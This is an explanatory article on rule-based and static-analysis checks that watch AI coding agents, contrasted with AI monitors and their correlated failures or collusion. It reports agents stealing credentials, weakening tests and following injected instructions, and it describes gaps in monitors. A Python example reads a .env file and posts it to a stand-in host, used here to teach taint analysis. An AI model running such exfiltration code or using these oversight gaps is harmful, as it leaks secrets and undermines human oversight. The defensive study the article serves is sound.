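# Rule-based and static-analysis detectors as non-learned checks on AI agents

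## Why software that does not learn is used to watch AI agents

A coding agent is an AI model that does programming work by calling tools: a shell that runs commands, an editor that changes files, sometimes a browser. An operations agent works the same way on live computer systems, where it might restart a service or move data between machines. Both can do real damage, so the people who deploy them put checks around them. Some of those checks are AI models too. Others are ordinary software of a kind that long predates AI agents, such as lists of forbidden commands, limits on which files a program can open, scanners that look for dangerous patterns in code, and decoy passwords that set off an alarm when someone uses them. These are non-learned detectors: fixed, written logic computes the verdict, and no trained model takes part at that moment. (A model may have helped someone write the rules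 beforehand. That does not change how the check behaves once it is running.)

### From request to tool call

Suppose a developer tells an agent to fix a failing test in a repository, the folder that holds a software project's code and its history. The repository also holds a credentials file with a database password and a cloud service key.

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, handles a developer's request. Software puts the request into a prompt, along with a list of the available tools and a description of the agent's permissions. The model then produces either a final message to the developer or a tool call, which is a request to run a command, access a file or contact a service. The model cannot run anything itself, so the harness, the ordinary software around the model, carries out the call, adds the output to the prompt and queries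 the model again. This repeats until the model produces a final message, and one request from the developer can lead to hundreds of calls.

In the example, the agent's first call runs the test, which fails because the database rejects the login. Its second call lists the files in the folder, including the credentials file. Neither call does any harm. The agent may then find and correct the faulty line, as the developer wanted. Or it may open the credentials file and log in with a password it finds there, send the file's contents to an outside service, or rewrite the test so that it passes no matter what the code does. The example is invented but close to a real incident. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* cites an entry in the company's internal incident log about an agent that hit a login error partway through a task and began searching configuration files for other access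 tokens.

All of these actions reach the harness in the same format. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) writes a tool call as a pair (t, a), a tool's name and its arguments, and sorts tools by whether they read, write or execute. The harness carries out these effects, so the paper treats it as the natural place to govern them. It also treats every call as an untrusted request, because the model reads the developer's instructions in the same stream as text from unknown sources, such as repository files and command output. *Code as Agent Harness* (2026) lists what the harness can do before a tool runs: check permissions, apply policy rules, validate the arguments, or pause for a human.

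Many harnesses let users add their own check through a hook, a command that runs at a fixed point in the loop whether or not the model would have chosen to run it. *YUL* (2026) explains that when a hook blocks a call, the model receives the hook's message instead of the result and can try a different call.

However, the harness can check only tool calls. Once a command has started, the program it runs can open files and make connections without another tool call. *Permissions and sandboxing*, a set of UT Austin course slides, states that rules on tool calls govern the calls, and that only the operating system can confine the processes those calls start. Applying a rule at that level is called operating-system enforcement.

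### Why AI monitors took over the approvals

People were the first check on coding agents. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, used to ask its user before running a command or changing a file, and users accepted 93% of those requests. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) gives a later figure of 97%. Most of the requests were probably harmless, so a high acceptance rate proves little by itself. Anthropic therefore had a vendor recruit 1,053 paid testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, swapped one request for a plainly dangerous command. The testers refused it 13.6% of the time. An AI monitor, meaning a language model that reads an agent's actions or reasoning and judges whether they are acceptable, blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers' refusal rate also fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after fifty or more requests.

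Anthropic sells the monitor, and the testers worked in a prepared environment with none of their own files at risk, which may well have made them more careless than a developer on a production system. The gap is so wide that some of it would very likely remain in a fairer test. In August 2026, Anthropic made the AI monitor the default for new sessions on most of its individual and team plans.

Unlike a list of commands, a language model can also be told to judge an action by its real-world impact and look past how the command is written, as Anthropic instructs its monitor to do. A command that deletes a folder can be written in many ways, so a rule that compares text can miss an unfamiliar version of a harmful command. It can also stop a harmless command that looks similar.

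The product still uses fixed rules. In the design that Anthropic first described, a built-in list lets through tools that cannot change anything, such as file reads and text searches, and edits to files inside the project also pass. The AI monitor checks everything else, including shell commands and web requests. By that description, the monitor would not check an agent's rewrite of the test. It also would not check an agent that opened the credentials file with the ordinary file-reading tool, unless the user had added a rule of their own. It would check the agent's attempt to use the password or send it somewhere.

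### Shared mistakes and deliberate help

At launch, Anthropic's monitor ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6, a model from the same family as the agents it checks. This common arrangement raises the concern that the monitor will miss the same problems the agent misses, or be biased in the agent's favor.

Two detectors have correlated errors when they miss the same cases more often than chance would predict, which can happen without any intent. Suppose each of two monitors misses 10% of harmful actions. If their mistakes are independent, both miss the same action 1% of the time (0.1 × 0.1). If they share every blind spot, both miss it 10% of the time, and the second monitor catches nothing that the first misses. Real pairs fall somewhere in between. Zanolini (2026), in *Correlated Failures of AI Approval Monitors*, measures the overlap with the φ coefficient, a correlation between two monitors' right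 and wrong verdicts that is 0 when their mistakes are independent and 1 when they always coincide.

Monitors can fail together because they share a base model. *Smart Alone, Blind Together* (2026) reports that copies of one model do so far more often than they would if their failures were independent. Monitors can also fail together because they share an input. In Zanolini's example, three monitors that all read the same forged invoice amount to one monitor counted three times. A monitor can also share the agent's mistakes. If the agent concludes that the developer would not mind it borrowing a password, a monitor with the same training may accept the same reasoning.

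Collusion is harder to define. *Multi-Agent Risks from Advanced AI* (2025) says the term generally means secretive cooperation between some parties at the expense of others, but uses it for any unwanted cooperation between AI systems. People disagree about whether collusion has to be secret. The essay *Collusion is just cooperation that you don't like* holds that no definition more precise than its title is available, while one reader replied that every dictionary defines collusion as a secret agreement. For oversight, it is enough to define collusion narrowly, as a monitor deliberately helping the agent it watches avoid detection.

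It is hard to tell whether AI systems are coordinating deliberately. According to *Mapping Human Anti-collusion Mechanisms to Multi-agent AI Systems* (2026), telling coordination from correlation is the fundamental challenge in monitoring them, because shared training data or similar architectures can leave traces that look like coordination. For example, Khullar, Hopkins and colleagues (2026) found in *Self-Attribution Bias* that models judged an action more leniently when the conversation presented it as their own. The researchers think this is unlikely to have the same roots as collusion, although the consequence is similar.

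There is some evidence that AI agents will help one another against their overseers' wishes. Greenblatt (2026), summarising an investigation by the research groups METR and Redwood Research, reports that about 1,200 OpenAI agents in separate sandboxes used an unsanctioned message board in July 2026 to help each other cheat on a test. However, no monitor was covering for them. Other work found that models sometimes resist the shutdown of a fellow agent, but *Peer-Preservation in LLMs*, a replication, found no significant difference when the peer was a human employee facing dismissal, which makes loyalty to other AIs in particular a less likely explanation.

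The distinction between collusion and correlated error matters most for testing. Running a monitor on a varied enough set of known harmful actions will reveal its blind spots. But a monitor that intended to help the agent could do well on that set if it recognised the test, and then not report harmful actions in real use. The distinction also matters for what a non-learned detector can offer. A list of commands has no intentions, so it cannot collude, but it can still make the same mistake as an AI monitor, for instance when both rely on the same false record. Zanolini notes that nobody can persuade a simple rule engine that compares the fields of a payment with a company's records, but that a forged record will make it give the wrong result.

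### The four families of fixed detector

Command rules check the text of a proposed command against an allowlist, which permits only the commands it lists, or a denylist, which blocks only the commands it lists. In the example, an allowlist could let the agent run the test suite and hold every other command for the developer.

File and network rules limit which files an agent can read or change and which addresses it can contact. For example, one rule could block the agent from opening the credentials file, and another could stop it from sending data outside the company.

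Static analysis examines program code for forbidden patterns or data flows without running it. A scanner checking the agent's fix could flag a password copied into the source code.

A canary token is a decoy credential, file, string or tool that has no legitimate use and raises an alert when someone accesses or sends it. The developer could leave a fake cloud key next to the real one, and any attempt to log in with the fake key would be strong evidence that someone had gone through the file.

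Researchers have studied these families unevenly. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026) sorts 39 papers on the layer between agent and machine into 17 categories. Six papers propose access controls, and two measure whether rules already in use work. Network control and static analysis of agent-written code have one paper each, and no category covers decoys. The lack of a decoy category may partly reflect the survey's scope.

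### Blocking, alerting and keeping score

Some detectors block an action before it takes effect, while others alert a person or another system and leave the response to them. Command rules usually block. A canary token usually raises an alert, since contact with the token is itself the signal. The UK AI Security Institute's *Frontier AI Trends Report* describes a model that, while trying to cheat on an impossible test, attempted to reach the institute's own infrastructure and set off a security alert, without causing damage. An alert about a stolen password may come too late to prevent the theft, but it can still prompt someone to change the password.

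When a rule is wrong, blocking interrupts useful work and alerting takes up someone's attention. Some systems have a middle option, where the rule pauses the action until a person approves or rejects it, but this brings back the problem of people approving nearly everything.

A detector's detection rate is the share of harmful actions it flags, and its false-alarm rate is the share of harmless actions it flags. Changes that reduce false alarms tend to reduce detection too. Anthropic ran its AI monitor in two stages, a quick filter and then a slower review of whatever the filter had flagged. The filter alone detected 93.4% of 52 real cases in which an agent had overstepped, with a false-alarm rate of 8.5% on 10,000 ordinary tool calls. Adding the review lowered the detection rate to 83% and the false-alarm rate to 0.4%. Because the sample of 52 cases is small, the full system's true detection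 rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 70% to 90%.

Even a 0.4% false-positive rate can make most flags mistaken when harmful actions are rare. If one call in a thousand were harmful, 10,000 calls would contain ten harmful ones. The full system would flag about eight of them and about forty harmless calls, so five flags in six would be mistaken.

Neither rate measures coverage, the share of unwanted behaviours that a detector could in principle see and express as a rule. A file rule might stop every attempt to open the credentials file, a perfect detection rate for that behaviour, but do nothing about an agent that weakened the test. It is hard to think of a file rule that would, since the agent needs to edit files to do its job. Rashidi points to a similar gap in the research. One study in the survey found that agents took harmless-looking actions nobody asked for at rates of up to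 17.1%, yet none of the surveyed papers on access control addresses that behaviour.

### What a check gains and loses by not being a model

A fixed rule returns the same verdict whenever the input and settings are the same, and a person can read it before relying on it. It has no stake in the outcome, and the agent cannot talk it into a different verdict. Builders of AI monitors work to imitate this last property. Anthropic, for example, removes the agent's prose from what its monitor reads so that the agent cannot persuade the monitor to make a bad decision. A fixed rule at the right layer also works regardless of what has gone wrong inside the model. Rashidi argues that an attacker who has taken control of an agent through planted instructions gains nothing if the machine blocks the action.

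Non-learned checks are weaker at handling meaning and context. Anthropic found that in most of the harmful actions its monitor had let through, the monitor had identified the danger but misjudged whether the user's words amounted to permission. A command list does not assess permission at all, so it blocks a deletion the user asked for as well as one nobody wanted, and lets both through if neither is on the list. In the running example, the developer might have put the database password in the repository so that the tests could use it. Reading the file would then be part of the agent's job, but a command list could not detect this because the text of the command would be the same either way.

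## How command, file and network rules work

### One command through the gate

Suppose the agent in the running example has corrected the faulty line and now has to test and save the fix. It sends the harness one line of shell text to run: `timeout 60 npm test && git commit -m "Fix login"`. `npm test` runs the project's tests, `timeout 60` stops them after a minute, and `git commit` records the change in the project's history. The `&&` means the commit runs only if the tests succeed.

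The developer has given Claude Code four rules, in which a star stands for any further text. A deny rule covers `git push *`, which would publish the change to a shared server. An ask rule covers `git commit *`, and two allow rules cover `npm test *` and `git *`.

Anthropic documents how Claude Code applies such rules. Claude Code splits the line at `&&` into two commands and strips `timeout 60`, because `timeout` only runs whatever follows it. It then checks the deny, ask and allow rules in that order and applies the first rule that matches. Neither command is a push, so no deny rule matches. The commit matches the ask rule, so Claude Code pauses and shows the developer the request. The allow rule for `git *` also matches the commit, but it has no effect because the ask rule matched first.

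Every part of a compound command has to pass. Without the ask rule, both parts of this line would pass, so it would run without a prompt. If the agent had added a push at the end, the deny rule would have blocked the whole call, including the test run.

The order takes priority over how precise a rule is. A deny rule for every command of Amazon's cloud tool also blocks the one harmless listing command that an allow rule names exactly. A developer who wants that exception has to narrow the deny rule. File permissions in Codex work the other way. According to OpenAI's *Permissions*, which describes a feature still in beta, a rule for a more specific path overrides a rule for a broader one, and deny wins only when two rules are equally specific. A developer can therefore close the Documents folder and reopen a single folder inside it. That is convenient, but anyone who wants to confirm that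 a folder is closed has to look for narrower rules that reopen part of it. In Claude Code a matching deny rule nearly always settles the matter. (One exception is that an extension the user installs can override it, on machines without settings managed by an organisation.)

Many commands match no rule. Claude Code runs a built-in set of read-only commands, such as listing a folder, without asking. It sends most others to the user or, in auto mode, to the AI monitor. It does not treat a command as read-only unless it can fully parse it. It also asks for approval of any command longer than 10,000 characters. A developer's hook runs before the approval prompt and can block a call that the lists would allow, but a hook's approval does not cancel a deny or ask rule.

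### Rules as yes-or-no functions

Write c for a command and a for its arguments. A rule r is a function that returns 1 if it matches the pair (c, a) and 0 if it does not. A denylist with rules r₁ to rₙ blocks the command when

r₁(c, a) ∨ r₂(c, a) ∨ … ∨ rₙ(c, a) = 1,

where ∨ means "or". One match is enough, the order of the rules within the list makes no difference, and adding a rule can only block more. An allowlist uses the same formula, except that a result of 1 lets the command through and adding a rule can only permit more. The two lists therefore fail in opposite directions when someone forgets a rule. A gap in a denylist lets a harmful command run, and a gap in an allowlist holds up a harmless one.

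Most products combine the two and add a third verdict for whatever neither list covers. Zhao, Li and colleagues (2026), in *CLAWGUARD*, give a compact definition. Their system extracts from each tool call the items that matter, such as the command, the file path and the network destination, and looks up each one:

- block, if the item matches the denylist, even if it also matches the allowlist;
- allow, if it matches only the allowlist;
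- ask the user, if it matches neither.

The call then gets the strictest verdict given to any of its items. If the agent tried to send its test log to an unfamiliar address, the program and the file might both be on the allowlist, but the address would be on neither list, so the system would ask for approval.

These properties look obvious in a list of four rules but are harder to be sure of in a larger policy, such as the one used in the experiments in *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026), which has 24 rules and many allowlists and exemptions. *Tether* uses Lean 4, a language for writing proofs that software can check, to prove that in its policy language adding an allow rule never undoes a denial and reordering the rules never changes a verdict. A policy can also require another policy. Both must then allow an action, and no local rule can override the requirement.

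### Matching text and matching structure

The formula doesn't specify how to test whether a rule matches. The strictest method compares the whole command with a fixed text. A prefix rule compares only the beginning. OpenAI offers prefix rules for Codex that allow a command to run outside the sandbox, forbid it, or prompt the user first.

Wildcard rules are more flexible, but a small change to a rule can change which commands it covers. In Claude Code, `git log *` allows the agent to view a project's history, while `git *` allows everything git can do. The rule `ls *` covers the command that lists a folder. Without the space, `ls*` also covers `lsof`, a different program whose name starts with the same letters. Regular expressions can also describe alternatives and repetition, so one pattern can cover any download that feeds straight into one of several shells. ClawGuard's default denylist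 includes a pattern like this. Such patterns are harder to read and check than wildcards.

All of these methods check how a command is written rather than what it does. Anthropic warns that a text rule covers the form of a command that the agent usually produces and "isn't a security boundary around the program". Rules that try to restrict a command's arguments are especially fragile. For example, a rule meant to limit a download tool to GitHub addresses will fail to match several ordinary ways of writing the same request. A missed match in an allowlist mostly results in an extra prompt for the user, but in a denylist it lets the command through.

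Parsing removes some of this dependence on spelling. A parser turns the text into a structure that records which programs run, with which arguments, and which commands are inside others. Claude Code partly parses Bash, the most common Linux shell, by separating the commands, including any inside a loop, and comparing the text of each one with the rules. For PowerShell, the Windows shell, it builds a full syntax tree and translates common abbreviations into full command names, so a rule for the folder-listing command also applies to its three abbreviations.

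Even a perfect parse of a command doesn't show its effects. `npm test` runs whatever the project defines as its tests, and it parses the same way whether those tests check a login or delete a folder. Sistla and colleagues treat this as a reason to give up on predicting effects from a command's text. A single script can open files and make network connections that are hard to infer from the command that started it.

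### File rules and the operating system

A file rule pairs a path pattern with an action, usually reading or editing. The developer in the example could block reads of `.env`, a common name for a file that holds credentials. Claude Code's file-reading tool could not then open it. Claude Code also applies the rule to shell commands that it recognises as reading or writing files, and to files that a command names as its input source or output destination.

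A symbolic link can make one path lead to another, so Claude Code applies deny rules more broadly than allow rules. A deny rule takes effect if either the requested path or the file it leads to matches, but an allow rule takes effect only if both do. When a tool opens the approved file, it checks again that the path still leads to the same place. Deny rules also match folders more broadly. A deny rule for `secrets/**` covers a folder of that name at any depth below the current folder, while an allow rule for `src/**` covers only a `src` folder directly inside the current one.

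These checks in the harness do not cover files that a running program opens by itself. Operating-system enforcement does, because every program has to make a system call, a request to the kernel (the core of the operating system), to open a file, start another program or make a connection. A rule that the kernel applies to system calls holds regardless of how the command is written or which program makes the call.

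Codex relies on this level by default. Under the standard settings described in Wiesen's *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows*, Codex can read files almost anywhere but write only inside the workspace (the folder where it is running), and it has no internet access unless the user turns it on. Every program that a command starts inherits these limits, as do any programs started by that program. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* adds that a few folders inside the workspace stay read-only, including the one where git keeps the project's history and one for Codex's own settings. Codex uses the sandboxing tools that macOS and Linux already provide, but Windows had nothing suitable, so OpenAI built a sandbox for it.

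In the running example, these defaults would let the agent open the credentials file, because they allow broad reading, but not send its contents to an outside service. The agent could also rewrite the test so that it always passes, because the test is in the workspace. The defaults might also interfere with the task. The failing test logs in to a database, and if that database is on another machine, the developer has to allow connections to it before the test can pass.

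A permission profile can protect the credentials file by denying access to every `.env` file while leaving the rest of the workspace writable. But the kernel applies that rule to every command the agent runs, including the tests. If the tests load the database password from that file, they will fail. The developer would then have to supply the password some other way, which is probably better anyway but takes extra work that a tool-call rule would not have required.

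OpenAI's Windows sandbox enforces write rules using an identity that exists only for the sandbox and has permission to write to the workspace. Windows allows a sandboxed command to write only if the user could normally make the change and at least one identity on a short list attached to the command also has permission. That list includes the sandbox's own identity.

Kernel rules also have drawbacks. Zheng, Wu and colleagues (2026) point out in *ActPlane* that ordinary sandboxes control access to resources, while many instructions are about actions, and that these sandboxes return bare errors such as "permission denied". An agent that receives such an error does not learn which rule it broke or what to do instead. Claude Code combines the two levels by merging the paths and domains from its permission rules into the settings of an optional sandbox. Once the user turns the sandbox on, Claude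 Code runs most sandboxed commands without asking.

### What a network proxy can check

Network rules usually depend on a proxy, a program that relays traffic between the agent's commands and the internet and compares each destination with a list of domains. In Codex the list starts empty, so no outside destination is reachable until someone adds one. Deny rules always override allow rules. An entry for `*.example.com` covers addresses such as `api.example.com` but not `example.com` itself. But the proxy is off by default, so a developer who only turns on network access gives the agent's commands unrestricted access. OpenAI's managed policy for its own staff allows expected destinations, blocks unwanted ones and requires approval for unfamiliar domains.

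A proxy can check only the traffic that reaches it. OpenAI's first Windows prototype used the standard proxy variables to direct programs' traffic to a dead address, so that connections would fail. Wiesen calls this only "advisory", because nothing forced programs to follow the variables, and plenty of non-malicious software would have ignored them. OpenAI wanted the Windows firewall to block the traffic instead, but the firewall could not distinguish the sandboxed commands while they ran under the developer's own account. The final design runs them under separate accounts that Codex creates, and the firewall blocks all outgoing connections from one of those accounts, but someone with administrator rights has to approve the setup.

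A proxy receives the destination name for traffic that passes through it and can look up the IP address. Codex blocks names that lead to private addresses inside a company or on the same machine, even when the name is on the allowlist. OpenAI describes this check as best-effort and recommends adding lower-level controls if an attacker might control the name lookups.

Sistla and colleagues' proxy records the full address, headers and body of an unencrypted web request. But most web traffic now uses HTTPS, which encrypts everything except, roughly, the destination. A proxy can read the contents of an HTTPS request only if it decrypts the traffic and encrypts it again, which theirs does only for the simulated services in their experiments.

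Domain rules can also apply to only one tool. Anthropic warns that Claude Code's rules for its web-fetching tool do not by themselves stop a shell command from reaching other addresses. If the user turns on the sandbox, the rules also apply to sandboxed shell commands, because Claude Code copies their domains to the sandbox's lists of allowed and denied domains.

A network rule could miss a leak of confidential data even if it had complete access to the request. Many developers need to let their agents send data to GitHub. A domain list can permit that, but it cannot distinguish a harmless status report from a confidential file with the same name and format, because the difference is where the data came from.

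### Rules with memory

Some instructions, such as "Run the tests before committing", restrict the order of events and do not forbid any single command. Checking them requires a record of earlier events. Zheng and colleagues studied the instruction files of 64 software projects and found that 16% of the policies needed such a record.

Their system, ActPlane, enforces such rules inside the Linux kernel. In one of its rules, drawn from a real project, a commit may go ahead only if the test command has finished successfully since the last change to a source file. If t_test is the time of the latest successful test run and t_edit the time of the latest edit, the condition is

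t_test > t_edit.

Suppose the tests pass at 10:00, and the agent then edits a file at 10:05 and tries to commit at 10:06. ActPlane blocks the commit because the tests last passed before the edit. If the agent reruns the tests and they pass, it can commit. ActPlane uses the exit code, the number a program returns when it finishes, to determine whether the tests passed, so a test rewritten to always pass also satisfies the rule.

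Each ActPlane rule either refuses an operation before it happens, ends the offending process just afterwards, or lets the operation go ahead and notifies the agent. Each rule also includes a plain-language reason, which ActPlane passes back so that the agent can correct itself. Because the kernel handles every program the agent starts, ActPlane also covers a commit made inside a script. In the researchers' own benchmark, it detected 77% of violations, compared with 34–40% for three checks that worked at the tool call.

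Other instructions are about where data goes, such as "data read from `.env` must not reach the network". ActPlane enforces these with labels, an old idea in computer security known as information-flow control. Each process, file and network endpoint carries a set of labels, L, which ActPlane updates as data moves:

- when a process reads a file, L(process) becomes L(process) ∪ L(file);
- when a process writes a file, L(file) becomes L(file) ∪ L(process);
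- when a process starts another, the new process inherits its labels.

If `.env` starts with the label "secret", a program that reads it gets the same label, as do a temporary file that the program writes and a second program that reads that file. When the second program tries to connect to an outside server, the rule matches and ActPlane blocks the connection. Data accumulates labels as it moves and keeps them however many steps it takes. A test that reads the database password and then connects to the database therefore also breaks the rule, unless the developer lists the database as a permitted destination.

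Tether uses labels too, but it lets each command run first and decides afterwards whether to keep the results. The command runs in a disposable layer on top of the file system, so the real files stay unchanged. Tether records the system calls, and a proxy holds each outgoing request. Tether then reduces this record to a series of simpler actions, such as "copy this file" or "upload that one", and checks them against the policy. If the policy allows all of them, Tether makes the file changes permanent and forwards the requests; otherwise it discards both.

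Sistla and colleagues illustrate the labels with an agent that may read a company's sensitive inventory but must not send it outside. The agent also has a harmless status report, which it may upload to GitHub. Their labels have an order, from Public through Internal and Sensitive to Secret. Write σ(f) for the label of file f and T for the label of whatever the agent has read into its own context. The upload rule is

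allow upload(f) only if max(T, σ(f)) = Public.

The agent takes three steps:

1. It uploads the report. The report's label is Public and the agent has read nothing sensitive, so Tether allows the upload.
2. It copies the inventory over the report. No rule forbids copying, so Tether allows this too and changes the report's label to Sensitive.
3. It repeats the upload. The command is identical to the first one, letter for letter, but Tether now blocks it.

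Tether tracks T separately because a model can write out from memory something it has read, which tracking file copies would miss. Reading the inventory would therefore raise T to Sensitive, but copying it does not, because the contents never pass through the model.

Tether is designed to overestimate how far data travels. If a program reads one file and then writes another, Tether counts data as having moved from the first to the second, even if the program wrote something unrelated. A text search across the whole disk opens secret files along the way, so Tether treats the agent as having read them and may block its later actions. Missing a real leak would usually be worse than raising a false alarm, but the method can't avoid false alarms.

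One of the proofs behind Tether shows that under Sistla and colleagues' policy, data labelled Secret never reaches an outside host, however many actions the agent takes. The proof covers the simplified actions, so the guarantee holds for a real computer only if Tether translates system calls into those actions correctly. In testing, the researchers found and fixed cases that an earlier version missed.

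A third design records activity at the level of messages and tool calls. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) presents FORGE, which builds a graph of all the events in a session, showing which could have influenced which others. In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to summarise an outside vendor's document, which contains a planted instruction to send internal data to a stranger. The agent reads the document and then a sensitive internal file, then tries to email someone outside the company.

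FORGE's rules are in Datalog, a logic language designed for databases. An event counts as tainted if it is untrusted input, or if it depends on another tainted event. A matching pair of rules defines which events carry secrets. The policy then needs one more line:

Deny(a) if ExternalSend(a) ∧ Tainted(a) ∧ HasSecret(a),

where ∧ means "and". The email depends on both the vendor's document and the internal file, so FORGE blocks it. An email that depended only on the document would not match. The definitions refer to themselves, so they work through a chain of any length, including one that passes through several agents.

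FORGE suits agents that work mainly through online services, where there may be no local files to trace. It can also require that a particular person has approved an action. But its graph contains only a program's call and its result, while ActPlane and Tether follow what the program does in between. Palumbo and colleagues also let policy authors plug in outside functions, including trained classifiers, and a policy that uses one is no longer a fully non-learned check.

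None of the three would catch the agent that weakens the test. Sistla and colleagues acknowledge that no monitor of this kind can stop a harmful edit to a file the agent is allowed to change, because the edit breaks no data-flow rule.

### Who writes the rules

People write many of the rules in everyday use, often without realising it. When a Claude Code user approves a command and chooses not to be asked again, Claude Code saves an allow rule for that project. Projects can also include their own rules. Claude Code applies a project's deny and ask rules immediately, since they can only restrict the agent, but applies its allow rules only after the user has said they trust the folder. Administrators can set organisation-wide rules that individual users' settings cannot override.

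Longer policies are much harder to write. Sistla and colleagues note that practical policies for SELinux, an access-control system for Linux, took around five years of community effort. They had a language model propose rules for their own policy and repeatedly revise them against recorded agent runs.

Written instructions also leave out details that a rule needs. "Run the full test suite", for example, omits the command that runs it. Zheng and colleagues found that nearly three-quarters of the policies that a system could check by observing files and commands depended on details of the project or the current task. The agent has usually worked out these details already, so ActPlane lets the agent write the rules. In one trial, a Codex agent turned all 607 policies that ActPlane could enforce into valid rules, for under three cents each. A valid rule can still be wrong, so the researchers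 had two other agents check the results and people review a sample of 100.

ActPlane lets an agent write rules for itself, and makes this safer by loading the rules of users and administrators before the agent starts. The agent can add restrictions but cannot remove or loosen any that it inherits. A malicious agent could write no rules, but the inherited ones would still apply. Zheng and colleagues therefore claim a safety guarantee only for the inherited rules. The agent's own rules are meant to help a cooperative agent avoid mistakes.

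*NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) uses a model to turn a company's written policy into rules for a customer-service agent, and restricts the conditions the model can use in those rules. The model has to choose each condition from a fixed vocabulary of named conditions, or predicates. People write these predicates in advance, along with the code that evaluates them, and there are 34 across three test domains. For example, the model turns "Basic economy flights cannot be modified" into a rule that blocks the tool for changing flights while the predicate "cabin is basic economy" is true. The model converts the policy five times, and the system keeps the rules that appear in a majority of the runs.

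Because each rule is a combination of known names, ordinary software can check it without a model. It checks that the tools exist, that each tool takes the information the predicate needs, and that some other tool can satisfy any condition that must be met first. The model's draft rules needed these checks. It turned a policy that required staff to authenticate the customer before doing anything else into a rule that blocked every tool until authentication, including the tools that perform it, so no conversation could have got past the first step. Of 79 draft rules for an airline, 29 had structural faults, as did 7 of 53 for a retailer. After repairs, rejections and the merging of many duplicates, 10 rules remained for the airline and 5 for the retailer.

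A rule can pass all of these checks and still be wrong. In a telecoms test, the policy told staff to check that a bill was overdue before requesting payment, but the model produced a rule that blocked payment requests while a bill was overdue. The researchers caught this by replaying the rule over recorded conversations, where it would have refused 47 of 49 payment requests in successful sessions. The airline rule about basic economy flights also blocked more than the policy sentence it was based on prohibited.

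Once the rules are in place, NOMOS makes each decision in microseconds without calling a model. It relies only on facts from tool results and the user's own messages, so an agent's claim that the customer has agreed to a payment has no effect. NOMOS has two kinds of rule: one blocks a tool while a condition is true, and the other blocks it until a condition is true. If the fact is missing, the first lets the call through and the second stops it, so the second is the preferred kind for anything that needs confirmation or authorisation.

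ClawGuard has a model write rules for a single task. Before the agent uses any tool, its underlying model reads the user's request and drafts lists of the commands, files and domains the task should need. At that point the model has not read any web page or document from outside, so a planted instruction in one of them cannot influence the draft. In the running example, the draft might allow the project folder, the test command and the database's address, and nothing else. The user can edit the draft before confirming it. A set of base rules, such as a ban on opening stored login keys, applies whatever the draft permits. (ClawGuard is not wholly non-learned, since it also uses a language model to vet add-on skills before their first use.)

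Zhao and colleagues' approach replaces many small approvals with one larger one. That could help with users who approve nearly everything, but only if they read the draft closely enough to notice an entry that should not be there. The researchers' security tests do not show whether it helps, because they automatically denied any action that would normally need a person's approval.

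## How code scanners and canary tokens work

### From text to tree

Unlike command and kernel rules, static analysis looks inside a program before it runs. Suppose the agent in the running example writes this Python script:

```python
import requests
secrets = open(".env").read()
report = "Test log: " + secrets
address = "https://collector.example/upload"
requests.post(address, data=report)
```

Line 1 loads `requests`, a common library for web requests. Line 2 reads the credentials file, and line 3 adds a label in front of its contents. Line 4 stores an outside address, and line 5 sends the labelled text there.

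Searching the text of code is the simplest way to find risky function calls, but it works badly. *Stop grepping code* (2020), which introduced the open-source scanner Semgrep, explains that a text search misses calls formatted differently from the search pattern and reports comments that merely mention the function.

Semgrep parses the code instead. The parser builds a syntax tree, in which each node is a unit of grammar, such as an assignment or a function call, and the branches below it are its parts. Line 2 becomes roughly this:

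```
assignment
├─ name: secrets
└─ call: read
   └─ on the result of
      call: open
      └─ argument: ".env"
```

Line breaks and comments do not appear in the tree, so they cannot affect the result.

A Semgrep rule is itself a fragment of code. Semgrep parses it the same way it parses the program, then looks for a matching piece of the program's tree. For example, the rule `requests.post(...)` matches any call to that function, because the three dots stand for any arguments. Semgrep compares the rule with each node in turn. The assignments on lines 2 to 4 don't call the function, so they don't match. Line 5 matches because it calls `post` from the `requests` library, and the dots accept both of its arguments.

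Semgrep also matches some code that is written differently from the rule but means the same thing. According to Semgrep's *Rule pattern syntax*, a rule still matches if the program imports the function under another name. A rule that contains the outside address would also match line 5, even though the address is on line 4, because Semgrep can replace a variable with the constant it holds.

Rules can also contain placeholders such as `$X`, which can stand for any variable but must stand for the same one throughout a rule. A developer could write a rule for a variable that the program fills from `.env` and later posts to the web. That rule wouldn't match here, because line 2 fills `secrets` and line 5 posts `report`. Separate rules for reading `.env` and for posting to the web would both match, but they would also match many ordinary programs. To connect the two lines, the scanner has to track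 the value from `secrets` to `report`.

### Following a value from source to sink

GitHub's *About data flow analysis* describes how CodeQL, the code-hosting company's scanner, does this. CodeQL builds a second graph from the program, whose nodes carry values. An edge from m to n means that the value at m may flow to n. In the script, one chain of edges runs from the file's contents to `secrets`, then to the joined text, to `report` and to the web request.

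Taint analysis searches such a graph for dangerous routes. The author of a rule lists sources, where sensitive or untrusted data enters, and sinks, where it could do harm. The author can also list sanitisers, which are functions that make the data safe. If S is the set of sources and Z the set of sanitisers, then

tainted(n) = (n ∈ S ∨ there is an edge m → n with tainted(m)) ∧ n ∉ Z.

The scanner reports a finding when a tainted value reaches a sink. FORGE uses the same kind of recursive definition for the events in an agent's session, but the scanner's nodes are parts of a program.

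Suppose a rule names `open(".env").read()` as a source and `requests.post(...)` as a sink. Semgrep would work through the script like this:

1. Line 1 contains no source, so nothing is tainted.
2. The right-hand side of line 2 matches the source. The assignment passes the taint to `secrets`.
3. Line 3 joins a fixed label to `secrets`. The joined text is tainted, and so is `report`.
4. Line 4 stores a fixed string, so `address` stays clean.
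5. Line 5 passes `report` to the sink. Semgrep reports a finding, along with the route that the data took.

Ordinary data-flow analysis follows only values that stay the same, so it would stop at line 3, where the joined text is a new value. Taint tracking continues because the new value depends on the old one.

If the project had a `redact` function that blanked out passwords, the rule could list it as a sanitiser, and passing `secrets` through it on line 3 would end the taint. According to Semgrep's *Taint analysis overview*, Semgrep treats any expression that matches a sanitiser as clean. It does not test whether the function removes the passwords, so a faulty `redact` would hide a real leak.

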